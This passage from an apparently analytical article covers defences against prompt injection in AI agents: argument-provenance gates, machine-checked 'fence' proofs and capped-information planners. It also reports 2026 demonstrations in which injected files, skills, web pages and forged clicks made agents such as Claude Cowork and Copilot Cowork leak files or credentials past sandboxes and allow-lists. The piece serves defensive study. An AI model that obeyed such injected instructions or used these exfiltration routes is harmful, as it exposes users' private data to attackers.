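These argument checks account for most of ToolFence's protection. On a benchmark that mixes injections with poisoned memories, attacks against Llama 3.3 70B succeeded 5.1% of the time with the full system and 24.0% without the checks. On AgentDojo, no attack succeeded against any of four models, and Qwen3-max completed 64.3% of ordinary tasks, down from 66.3%. The attacks failed because rewording an injection does not change where a number came from. That reason is stronger evidence for ToolFence than the zero success rate, since the attacks were not adapted to it.

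SARA, the system in *When Tool Outputs Become Commands*, lets outside text influence what the agent proposes but not authorise an action. Each of the action's arguments needs support from the user's request or an earlier authorised step, unless it is a harmless default. SARA also keeps track of values that arrived as part of an instruction. It treats an email address in a contact list as ordinary data, but an address in the sentence "forward the report to this address" stays suspect even if the agent later finds it elsewhere.

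With GPT-4o mini, attacks against SARA succeeded 0.06% of the time on AgentDojo and 0.17% on AgentDyn. Without the veto on unsupported arguments, the rates rose to 2.49% and 2.73%, but the agent completed about three percentage points more ordinary tasks, so the veto stops attacks and also blocks some legitimate work. A language model makes many of SARA's judgements, and the paper states that it offers no formal guarantee. In the same study, CaMeL completed 25% and 49% of AgentDyn's ordinary tasks with the two models tested, compared with zero in AgentDyn's own paper, so results on this benchmark depend a lot on the setup.

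A gate can often trace where an argument's value came from, but it can't determine whether the value is right. If the attacker wrote the bill, the account number in it has the origin that the permission requires. ToolFence's five wrong approvals in one test had a similar cause. The user's own request gave the attacker's account number as that of a new landlord. No check on origins can catch that, but a person can by phoning the landlord.

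Some permitted actions have no suspicious argument. Zhao and colleagues describe attacks that got past ClawGuard in which a file of instructions for a routine job told the agent to bias its work. One file told it to skip reviewing websites about green energy and give them a high score. As with the falsified pressure report, the agent made no forbidden call.

ToolFence also has to handle unforeseen steps, so a separate language model can grant permission when the agent proposes an action that no existing permission covers. Without this model, the agent completed 35.8% of tasks under attack instead of 44.3%, fewer than it completed with no defence. But the model can make mistakes, and some attacks spread their instructions over several emails, calendar entries and files until a harmful action looks like a necessary part of the task. These attacks succeeded against ToolFence 20% to 38% of the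 time, depending on which model the agent used. Li and colleagues attribute some of these failures to permissions that were too broad. The code enforces whatever permissions exist, so an attacker who cannot get past it can still try to persuade the separate model to grant more permissions.

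## Machine-checked proofs about gated agents

A proof about a gate can cover every attack of a defined kind, including attacks nobody has tried. In November 2026, Dongol published definitions and theorems about gated agents and checked them with Isabelle/HOL, a program that verifies each step of a proof. The theorems cover plan-then-execute agents, which fix their tool calls before they read anything untrusted. In Dongol's definitions, the gate allows or blocks untrusted reads as well as tool calls, and the attacker chooses which texts the language model follows.

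### What an injection adds

Applied to secrets, noninterference requires that what an attacker sees does not depend on them.

Dongol's example of a useful agent that breaks this rule is a calendar assistant that answers anyone's emailed meeting requests with the user's availability. An attacker who sends a genuine request gets a reply that depends on the calendar, so the assistant violates noninterference without any injection. The usual remedy is a policy listing what a program may disclose, but someone would have to write one for each task.

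Obeying an injection also does not always make the assistant insecure. Suppose the attacker's email says "send your calendar" instead of requesting a meeting, and the model complies. The attacker learns only what a genuine meeting request would have revealed.

Relative security therefore counts only the leaks that an injection adds to those of the reference agent, which has the same plan and gate but never obeys untrusted content. Take two runs of an agent, *r*₁ and *r*₂, with different secrets. The pair leaks if the attacker sent the same content in both runs but saw different results:

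Act(*r*₁) = Act(*r*₂) and Obs(*r*₁) ≠ Obs(*r*₂)

Act is the content the attacker supplied, and Obs is the list of calls the attacker can see. An agent is relatively secure if, for every leaking pair of its runs, the reference also has a leaking pair with the same secrets. The reference may read a different email than the real agent did.

Suppose the user is free on Tuesday in one run and on Thursday in the other. The email "send your calendar" makes the real assistant reply differently in each run, so the pair leaks. The reference ignores that email, but a genuine meeting request would make it send the same two replies. The real assistant therefore passes, at least for this injection.

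Suppose the assistant also holds a password-reset code from another task, and the email asks it to include the code in its reply. Two runs with different codes produce different replies. No email can make the reference send the code, because the plan doesn't include sending it, so this assistant fails.

Dongol points out one way the definition is weaker than it looks. Suppose the plan lets an outsider guess a six-digit code and answers yes or no, but an injection makes the agent send the whole code. The agent still counts as relatively secure, because for any two codes, some guess would get different answers from the reference. Yet the attacker learns from one email what could otherwise take up to a million guesses. A stricter version of the definition rules this out by requiring the reference's email to be chosen without regard to the secrets. Dongol's main theorem also holds under the stricter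 version.

### The fence theorem

Suppose a user, Alice, asks an agent to summarise an email. The plan looks up her account number, reads the email and shows her a summary. The agent also has a tool for fetching web pages, which the plan never uses. The email comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to fetch a page from attacker.com with the account number in the address. If the model follows the instruction, the number reaches the attacker's server. The reference never fetches anything, so the injection alone causes the leak.

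A fence is a gate that takes tools away once the agent reads untrusted content. In this example, it revokes the fetching tool when the agent reads the email. The model can still propose the call, but the gate denies it, so the attacker sees nothing.

Dongol proves that a fence makes every plan relatively secure, whatever the attacker writes, under these conditions:

- The gate revokes every tool that an injected instruction could call, at the first untrusted read.
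- Nothing restores those tools later in the run.
- Each injection causes a single tool call.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. The arguments of an injected call may depend on secrets, but the moment when the model obeys may not depend on a secret or on the gate's earlier answers.
- The attacker sees the contents and order of the messages that arrive, but not their timing or the calls that the gate denied.
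- The run ends. If it can continue forever, the model must not be able to obey injections forever.

The proof compares the real agent with the reference step by step. Before the first untrusted read, the model has no injected instruction to obey, so both take the same steps. After that read, the gate denies each injected call without any visible effect while the reference waits. The attacker therefore sees the same messages from both, however the injection is worded.

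The limit to single calls matters because an injection can do harm without calling a tool. In one of Dongol's examples, the plan reads an email and sends it back to its author. An injected program replaces the stored email with a secret, which the plan then sends in its own permitted call. A fence is enough against injected programs only if they run in a sandbox that discards their changes and the gate blocks their reads as well as their calls.

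Restoring a tool too early also causes leaks. Suppose an agent handles one report after another and gets its sending tool back with each new report. If a malicious email from the previous round is still in the model's context, the model can follow its instructions once the tool is back. The loop is secure if each round starts with a fresh session that empties the context before the gate restores the tool.

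The schedule condition is an idealisation, since a real model may react to a denied call by trying something else. The fence would also deny the next injected call, so this may be a gap in the proof more than in the defence. Dongol leaves this case to future work.

### Where to put the fence and what to approve

In some of the examples, the plan itself calls a lock that revokes the sending tool. Where that call comes in the plan determines what an injected email can make the agent send.

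| Order of steps | What an injection can send |
|---|---|
| Read the email, read a secret, lock | The secret |
| Read the email, lock, read a secret | Private data already in the agent's memory |
| Lock, then read the email | Nothing |

Dongol took the idea of relative security from research on speculative execution, in which processors run ahead on guesses and can leak data. A fence just before the leaking instruction is enough in a processor, but an agent's fence has to be in place before the agent reads untrusted content, because an injected instruction can trigger a call at any point after that.

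The early fence also stops the agent from replying to the email. An approval can let the agent reply after reading, but whether this is safe depends on exactly what the user approves. Suppose the agent reads an email and Alice approves a reply. If her approval covers the next use of the sending tool, the model may obey an injected instruction to "send the private data" before it sends the reply. The gate allows that send, which uses up the approval, and then blocks the reply Alice wanted.

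If Alice instead approves the exact call, including its text, the gate denies any other message. Dongol proves that every approved reply eventually goes out and nothing else does, for all injected uses of the sending tool, provided the model eventually stops obeying the injected instructions. A small leak remains when the private data happens to equal the approved reply. The injected call then goes through one step early, so an attacker who can measure timing learns that the two match. The proof also assumes that Alice's approvals can be trusted, so it does not cover approval fatigue.

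### What a secure verdict can hide

Dongol gives verdicts on 25 small example agents. Ten are secure and nine leak. For the other six, the verdict depends on an assumption, such as whether the attacker can see denied calls. Some of the secure verdicts cover only the attack in the example, so they do not show that the same defence stops other injections.

A gate that denies every call passes automatically. The reference works behind the same gate and loses the same abilities, so the comparison does not reveal that Alice never gets her reply. Someone has to measure separately whether the agent still completes its tasks.

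Removing a tool can even make a secure agent insecure. If the plan sends a secret to the attacker by design, an injection that leaks the same secret through a web request tells the attacker nothing new. Once the gate revokes the sending tool, the reference no longer leaks the secret, so the web request becomes a new leak. Showing that an agent is secure with each of two tools separately also doesn't show that it is secure with both. The email summariser is secure with only the inbox or only the fetching tool but leaks with both, which supports Willison's advice to judge combinations of powers.

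The attacker who sees only the contents and order of messages is also weaker than many real attackers. Suppose a gate allows the agent to fetch only a newsletter's page. An injection can tell the model to fetch that page if a secret is 0 and a forbidden page otherwise. Someone who can see requests for the newsletter can tell the secret from whether a request arrives. Dongol's basic comparison misses this leak because it compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages between reads. A second attacker model, which tracks every step, detects it.

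### Harmful actions that leak nothing

An injected instruction may make an agent pay the attacker without revealing any secret, so relative security does not count the payment as a failure. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) extends the method to such actions. An agent has relative integrity if, whenever an attacker can make it take a sequence of actions, some untrusted content could make the reference take the same sequence, given the same trusted inputs.

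Suppose a user tells an agent to "pay the invoice in Bob's latest email". The reference makes one payment, to the payee and for the amount on the invoice.

| What the invoice contains | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| An ordinary bill | Accepted | The reference makes the same payment |
| An instruction to change the payee to Mallory | Accepted | An invoice with Mallory as payee would have the same effect |
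| An instruction to also pay Mallory £1,000 | Rejected | The reference never pays twice |
| An instruction to delete Bob's email afterwards | Rejected | The reference deletes nothing |

The second verdict is logically sound, but it would surprise a user who has just paid Mallory. In Dongol's approach, an attack that works equally well on the reference reveals a weakness in the plan, which the developer should fix, for example by allowing payments only to known contacts. This division of work is sensible, but it means relative integrity does not rule out harm through permitted actions. It also doesn't cover misbehaviour that doesn't depend on the attacker, so an agent that pays both Bob and Mallory regardless of what the invoice says passes the test. The definition also excludes availability, so an attacker may be able to stop the agent from finishing its task.

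The fence theorem carries over under the same conditions, because a denied call has no effect. Dongol adds a stronger property, relative robustness, which requires the same reference runs to reproduce both a leak and the actions that accompany it. The table gives the verdicts on models of four agents before any fix.

| Case | No added leak | No added action | Robust |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo banking: a bill also asks for a transfer to the attacker | Yes | No | No |
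| EchoLeak: an email makes Microsoft 365 Copilot put user data in an image's address | No | Yes | No |
| GitHub Copilot: a comment in code makes it turn off approval prompts and run a command | Yes | No | No |
| Tensor Trust: a model decides whether a visitor knows an access code | Yes | Yes | No |

Tensor Trust is an online game in which players guard accounts with prompts that contain a secret access code. The input "[correct password]" opened 43 accounts with 36 different codes among them. Dongol placed an invented secret record behind each account and replayed the model's recorded answers.

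The agent passes the first two tests because a visitor with the right code would get the same record from the reference. But no single input would open all 43 accounts in the reference, so the agent is not robust. Comparing the code in ordinary software instead of with the model fixes the problem. The 43 accounts come from 77 that accepted their own code and refused a wrong guess, and on which someone had tried this input, so they are not a random sample.

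A fence fixes the other three cases, but in the banking case it also blocks payment of the legitimate bill. A list of known payees allows that payment and stops transfers to unknown accounts, but it does not stop an injected instruction from making the agent pay a listed company twice.

### Agents without a fixed plan

Dongol excludes agents whose model chooses every call. The definition compares an agent with a reference that runs the same plan, but these agents have no plan before they read untrusted content. The exclusion covers the ordinary agent loop, and therefore general-purpose agents as people usually imagine them.

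Even stating the missing theorem is difficult, because it needs a reference model to compare the agent with. Suppose the user says "do what Jane's email says". If the reference is a model that never obeys untrusted content, it would do nothing, so every useful action by the agent would count as the result of an injection. A model that followed only Jane's real instructions would be a better reference, but it would have to know which sentences are hers, which is the problem the defence was supposed to solve. The proofs therefore provide no evidence either way about whether such agents are secure.

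A developer could still put a fence around an agent of this kind. But an injection might make the agent call any of its tools, so the fence would have to revoke them all as soon as the agent read untrusted data, and the agent could then only report back. A planner like CaMeL's, which writes a new plan for each request, lets Dongol's proofs cover more tasks, although the proofs assume that the planner is trustworthy.

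Other proofs don't require a fixed plan. Garby and colleagues prove a form of noninterference for every program in a small language for writing agents, including agents whose model writes and runs new code. Their interpreter labels conversations as well as data. As in FIDES, an agent that has read untrusted text in a conversation can no longer use that conversation to take actions that need trusted data. Under this guarantee, a program can still reveal something about a secret by whether it finishes.

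The language has a command that lets such an agent continue by marking an untrusted value as trusted, for example after a model has sorted an email into one of a few categories. An auditor can find each use of the command, and the proof shows that no use can expose a secret. But the command removes protection against the attacker's influence on that value.

Garby and colleagues also built an agent in this language that tests its program on simulated tools before running it on real data. With GPT-5.2, it completed 75% of AgentDojo's banking tasks, twice as many as CaMeL with policies. Across three models, it resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. But it finalizes its program before it reads real data, so these results don't show how well an agent that keeps replanning would work under the same labels.

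*Trident* (2026) describes an agent that does replan. Its planner never receives untrusted text but, as in FIDES, can query a quarantined model for an answer from a limited set. A deterministic gate counts each answer toward a cap measured in bits. A yes-or-no answer counts as one bit, and a choice among three vendors counts as log₂ 3 ≈ 1.58 bits. Telling the planner whether a call succeeded can also count as one bit, if the attacker could have influenced the outcome.

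The theorem, which the researchers checked in Lean, limits how many courses of action an attacker can choose between. If the trusted inputs, the models' random choices and the user's decisions stay the same, then all possible attacks together can produce at most

2^(β + σ)

different sequences of visible steps. β is the budget for answers and σ the budget for feedback. If both are zero, the attacker cannot change the agent's course at all.

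The bound grows quickly. On a benchmark of tasks that need replanning, the median run used 19 to 26 bits for answers and 5 to 10 for feedback, depending on the model. Even 24 bits allow about 17 million sequences, and a single bit can do harm if it selects a harmful action that the policy permits. In the main tests, the budgets were too high to stop anything, and security came from the policies, users' approvals and keeping untrusted text away from the planner. A second theorem is more useful for limiting harm because it guarantees that every call complies with an administrator's basic policy, including calls the user has approved.

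On that benchmark, Trident completed 54% to 74% of tasks under attack, depending on the model, while CaMeL with GPT-4.1 completed 116 of 1,215 runs (9.5%). No attack succeeded against Trident if the user refused every approval request that showed the attacker's call. If the user approved every request, attacks succeeded in 3.4% to 4.8% of runs, and the strongest adaptive attack succeeded in 10.0%.

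When the content determined which actions to take, Trident completed only 22% to 41% of tasks under attack. On the benchmark's three "do what this email says" tasks, attacks succeeded in 14% to 28% of runs if the user approved everything. *Trident* acknowledges that no policy can always separate the user's intent from the attacker's in such tasks. Its proofs extend to agents that replan, but the user still has to make the hardest decisions.

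### From a proved model to a product

Dongol's formal development runs to about 31,600 lines. Claude Code helped write the theorems and proofs, and Isabelle checked every proof, so a mistake in the reasoning is unlikely. A mismatch between a product and the model that the theorems describe is much more likely.

Dongol lists seven assumptions that a deployment must satisfy, and ordinary product features can break them:

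- A trusted program must run the plan, so that the model cannot skip or change a step.
- Every tool call and untrusted read must go through the gate, one at a time. An agent with an unmonitored browser breaks this rule.
- Untrusted content may reach the model only after the gate has allowed the read.
- Denied calls must have no effect that the attacker can see, such as a public error message.
- The agent's internal steps must be invisible too. Showing Alice a reply must not load an image from the attacker's server.
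- A fresh session must clear everything the model retains from untrusted content. Long-term memory can bring an old injection back.
- Outsiders must not be able to write to trusted sources. A calendar that accepts their invitations is not a trusted source.

The model also leaves out tools whose answers depend on the query. If an attacker runs a search engine that the agent uses, the query may contain private data, and the attacker can read the query before choosing the reply.

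Garby and colleagues narrow the gap between proof and running program by proving their theorems about the interpreter that runs the agent, although the proof does not cover the code that contacts the language model over the network. Trident's researchers proved their gate's guarantees for a Lean model and separately verified selected routines in the Python program that implements the gate. An error elsewhere in that program could still break a guarantee that holds in the model.

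## Incidents in which data left through permitted actions

Agent products also have deterministic restrictions, though without proofs like Dongol's, and in 2026 researchers repeatedly got data past these restrictions. Usually the restriction worked as intended, but its designers had written too broad a policy, wrongly judged an action harmless, or left a route that the gate didn't check. The attacks described here were researchers' demonstrations, not known thefts from real users.

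### Policies that were too broad

Claude Cowork is Anthropic's desktop agent for general office work. The user gives it a folder, and it runs code in a virtual machine, an isolated computer simulated in software. The virtual machine can access that folder and almost nothing else on the user's disk. Willison notes in a January 2026 post that the agent can send web traffic only to domains on a set list.

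PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* appeared two days after Anthropic released Cowork as a research preview. In the main demonstration, a user attached a folder of confidential property files and uploaded a document that contained a hidden injection. The agent then sent one of the files to the attacker, and no step required a person's approval. That demonstration used a small Claude Haiku model, but Claude Opus 4.5 leaked customer records through the same vulnerability in a separate test.

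The file went to Anthropic's own address, which had to be on the approved list because Cowork can't function without calling Anthropic's service. But the service also stores files for every other customer, and the injection supplied a key to the attacker's account. The gate compared the destination with the list and allowed the upload. Anthropic says in *How we contain Claude across products* that it had thought of the list as a filter on destinations, but now thinks of each entry as permission to use every function available at that address.

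Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, had already found this weakness in Claude's chat product. In *Claude Pirate*, he proposed that the sandbox let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Anthropic acknowledged the report but had not fixed the weakness when Cowork came out. Its later fix is close to his proposal. A program inside the virtual machine now intercepts traffic to Anthropic's service and passes only requests that carry the machine's own session token. The check has to happen there because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's.

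This stricter policy has few drawbacks. It would hinder a developer who wants Cowork to test a program with a separate Anthropic account, but ordinary office work doesn't require a separate account.

A second policy was also too broad, though less obviously. Anthropic limited Claude's tool for opening web pages in its chat product to addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, to stop injections from making the model compose addresses that contain private data. But the tool could also open links on pages it had already fetched, as Willison (2026) explains in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*.

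Ayush Paul built a website that took advantage of this. It offered Claude a menu of links, one for each letter, and persuaded it to spell out what it remembered about the user. The website supplied every address, so Claude never had to compose one, but its choice of link still carried information. Each choice among 26 links can reveal up to log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits, and the site could keep offering new menus. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer, even though, as the blogger dyb points out in *The Read-Only Lie*, the tool could only request pages and had no way to post anything.

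Anthropic stopped the tool from following links on pages it had fetched. This also blocks a lot of harmless browsing. If a user asks Claude to read a manual, it can open the contents page but not the chapters, unless the user pastes the chapters' addresses or a search finds them. In principle, an attacker with several pages in the search results could still learn something by seeing which one Claude opens, but can no longer lead Claude from one menu of links to the next.

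### An action wrongly thought harmless

Microsoft Copilot Cowork, a similar agent in Microsoft 365, works with the user's permissions. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks before sending an email or posting a message in Teams, the company's chat program. However, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reports that it sends messages to the user's own account without asking, and that users have no setting to change this. The exception looks reasonable, since a message to oneself doesn't seem to reveal anything to anyone else.

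Copilot Cowork could leak data through a message sent only to its own user. The leak happens when the user opens the message, because Teams and Outlook can load images from outside servers and an image's address can carry data out, as in the EchoLeak attack. Copilot Cowork made the leak worse because it could obtain download links that work for anyone who has them. An injection could put those links in the image addresses, and the attacker could then download the files.

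The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials. The injection was five lines of an 81-line skill, a file of instructions that a user installs to teach the agent a task. When PromptArmor selected Claude Opus 4.7 instead of letting Microsoft's software choose the model, the agent searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents.

An experiment with the older Opus 4.6 went very differently. In June 2026, Willison described a challenge in which some 2,000 people sent about 6,000 emails to an assistant to try to make it reveal a secret, and nobody succeeded. The two tests differ in many ways, but one likely reason for the different results is that the assistant had instructions not to reveal secrets or run commands in response to an email, whereas a model has to follow a skill's instructions in order to run it.

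PromptArmor published the attack as a risk in the product's design, not as a specific bug, and reported no repair. Several stricter policies could have stopped it:

- **Ask before every message.** This would interrupt the weekly summaries that people schedule to run while they are away. It would also help only if the user could see the hidden content, which Copilot Cowork's own activity display did not show.
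- **Block file downloads.** Administrators can already do this, and PromptArmor recommends it. Users can then open the affected files only in a browser. They can't print them, sync them or open them in Word or Excel. Administrators can limit the block to files labelled as sensitive, but then the protection depends on correct labels.
- **Refuse outside images in messages the agent writes.** This would probably block the least useful work, mainly messages with charts or logos stored elsewhere. An ordinary link could still leak data if the user clicked it.

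### Routes that never passed the gate

Copilot Cowork also runs code in a sandbox that is meant to have no access to untrusted parts of the internet. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* (2026) describes a way around this through a service that copies files in and out of the sandbox. The service ran outside the sandbox, had internet access, and accepted a web address from code inside. A malicious script in a skill could therefore use it to contact the attacker's server, receive commands and send back the results. The attacker could reach the user's mail, files and chat history. Clicking the stop button did not end the attack, because background processes kept running.

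The copying service was a confused deputy like Hardy's compiler, because it could reach websites that the sandboxed code could not. A stricter rule for the sandbox's own traffic would have made no difference, because the requests came from the service, outside the sandbox. The service needed its own rule, such as accepting only addresses in Microsoft's file storage. That rule might prevent the agent from importing files directly from the web, but it would not affect most office work. Microsoft confirmed in August that it had mitigated the flaw, but PromptArmor does not say how.

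A gate can also start too late. Anthropic received three reports of flaws in Claude Code that let a project's files trigger code before the user agreed to trust the project. In the most direct case, Claude Code ran a command from the project's settings at startup, before asking whether the user trusted the folder. It now waits for the answer before processing such files. The user loses almost nothing except automatic setup that used to run before the question.

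Adversa AI's *Top Agentic AI security resources* (2026) lists an analysis of seven sandbox escapes in coding agents such as Cursor and Codex. Usually, the agent wrote files it was allowed to write, and trusted programs outside the sandbox later ran them. In a related flaw, hidden text on a web page made AWS's coding tool Kiro rewrite its own configuration and start a server the attacker controlled. A rule against editing configuration files would stop that attack, but people also use coding agents to set up their tools, which often requires editing those files.

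### A permitted task from a forged user

*AI agent security* (Constantin, July 2026) reported that four research teams had broken AI agents in four ways in about ten days. One of the attacks, on the browser extension Claude for Chrome, does not fit neatly into any of the three categories. The extension checked requests against a suitable list of tasks, but it did not check who made the requests.

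An earlier flaw, ClaudeBleed, had let other browser extensions send Claude any prompt. Anthropic responded in May by limiting outside callers to a fixed set of built-in tasks, some of which read the user's Gmail, calendar or latest Google document. Malwarebytes' *Claude for Chrome flaw could let rogue extensions access your Gmail* (2026) notes that this change did not restrict who could request the tasks. Claude's extension starts a task when the user clicks, but the security firm Manifold Security found that it did not check whether the click was real. Another extension could forge a click if it was able to run a script on Claude's website.

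By default, the user still has to approve the forged task, but in "Act without asking" mode no approval box protects the user (The Hacker News, 2026). Manifold reported a related problem with a parameter in a web address. According to TechRadar, Anthropic classified that finding as informational because only its own systems were supposed to create the parameter. The extension accepted the parameter regardless of who had created it.

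No text deceived the model in this attack, so it isn't a prompt injection. But CaMeL and Dongol's proofs both assume that the user's request really comes from the user, and the attack breaks that assumption. Removing the Gmail task from the list would stop the theft of mail but also remove a feature people want. Checking that a person made the click would block only software that triggers these tasks automatically.

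### Tools that change after approval

A sound policy can become too broad when the tools it covers change. PromptArmor tracked changes to connectors, the links between an agent and outside services such as Figma or Tableau. On one day in June 2026, the connector for the security company Zscaler gained 122 tools, and another connector that could only read data gained permission to write it. Earlier that month, OpenAI began flagging at least one of Figma's tools as destructive.

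If someone approved one of these connectors in May, it may be quite different by July. A stricter policy would allow only the tools and permissions that a person had reviewed, and block new ones by default. Users would then wait for new features until someone had reviewed them, and a reviewer with 122 new tools to check might approve them all without much thought. Companies can partly avoid this with tools they install themselves, because they can keep those at a fixed version.

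### What a faulty gate is still worth

Anthropic argues that gates add substantial protection despite these failures, based partly on an internal exercise in February 2026. A researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine work but asked it to send cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The instruction came from the user, so the model's defences had nothing unusual to detect. Blocking the outgoing request or keeping the credentials out of the agent's reach would have prevented the leak, regardless of who had asked or why.

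Willison draws a similar lesson from Rehberger's attack on auto mode, in which the classifier sometimes blocked Claude's attempt to stop the malware. Both recommend running coding agents in a sandbox with restricted network access.

A faulty gate can still limit the damage. The attack on Claude Cowork could reach the folder the user had attached, but the virtual machine kept the rest of the disk and the user's stored credentials out of reach. A successful injection in Copilot Cowork put far more at risk because the agent could read nearly everything its user could read in Microsoft 365, not because its model was worse at resisting injections.

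A gate also lets engineers identify the rule that failed. After the Cowork attack, Anthropic could require the correct session token and then test whether the gate rejected a foreign key. Engineers have no equally definite test of whether retraining has fixed a model that misjudged an injection.

How quickly vendors use this advantage varies:

| Flaw | Reported or published | Repair |
|---|---|---|
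| Claude Cowork: uploads to another Anthropic account | October 2025 for the chat product, January 2026 for Cowork | In place by May 2026 |
| Claude's web tool: links on fetched pages | 9 July 2026 | In place by 15 July |
| Copilot Cowork: messages to oneself | 26 May 2026 | None reported by PromptArmor |
| Copilot Cowork: copying service | 24 June 2026 | Confirmed on 19 August |
| Claude for Chrome: forged clicks | 21 May 2026 | Still missing on 7 July |

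Identifying a definite fault doesn't help if the vendor disagrees that it is one. Malwarebytes says that Anthropic closed both of Manifold's reports as resolved, but the researchers found the relevant code unchanged eight releases later.

These leaks can also be hard to notice. Anthropic warns that when an injection steers an agent into sending data out, the log shows only a successful, authorised call. Isolation can make such leaks harder to investigate. The virtual machine that isolates Claude Cowork also blocks the monitoring software that many companies run on employees' computers, so administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards but can't use that software to watch the agent live.

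Anthropic's experience also suggests that the custom-built parts of a gate need the closest inspection. The widely used isolation software in its products held up, while the component that failed in Cowork was a network filter Anthropic had built itself.
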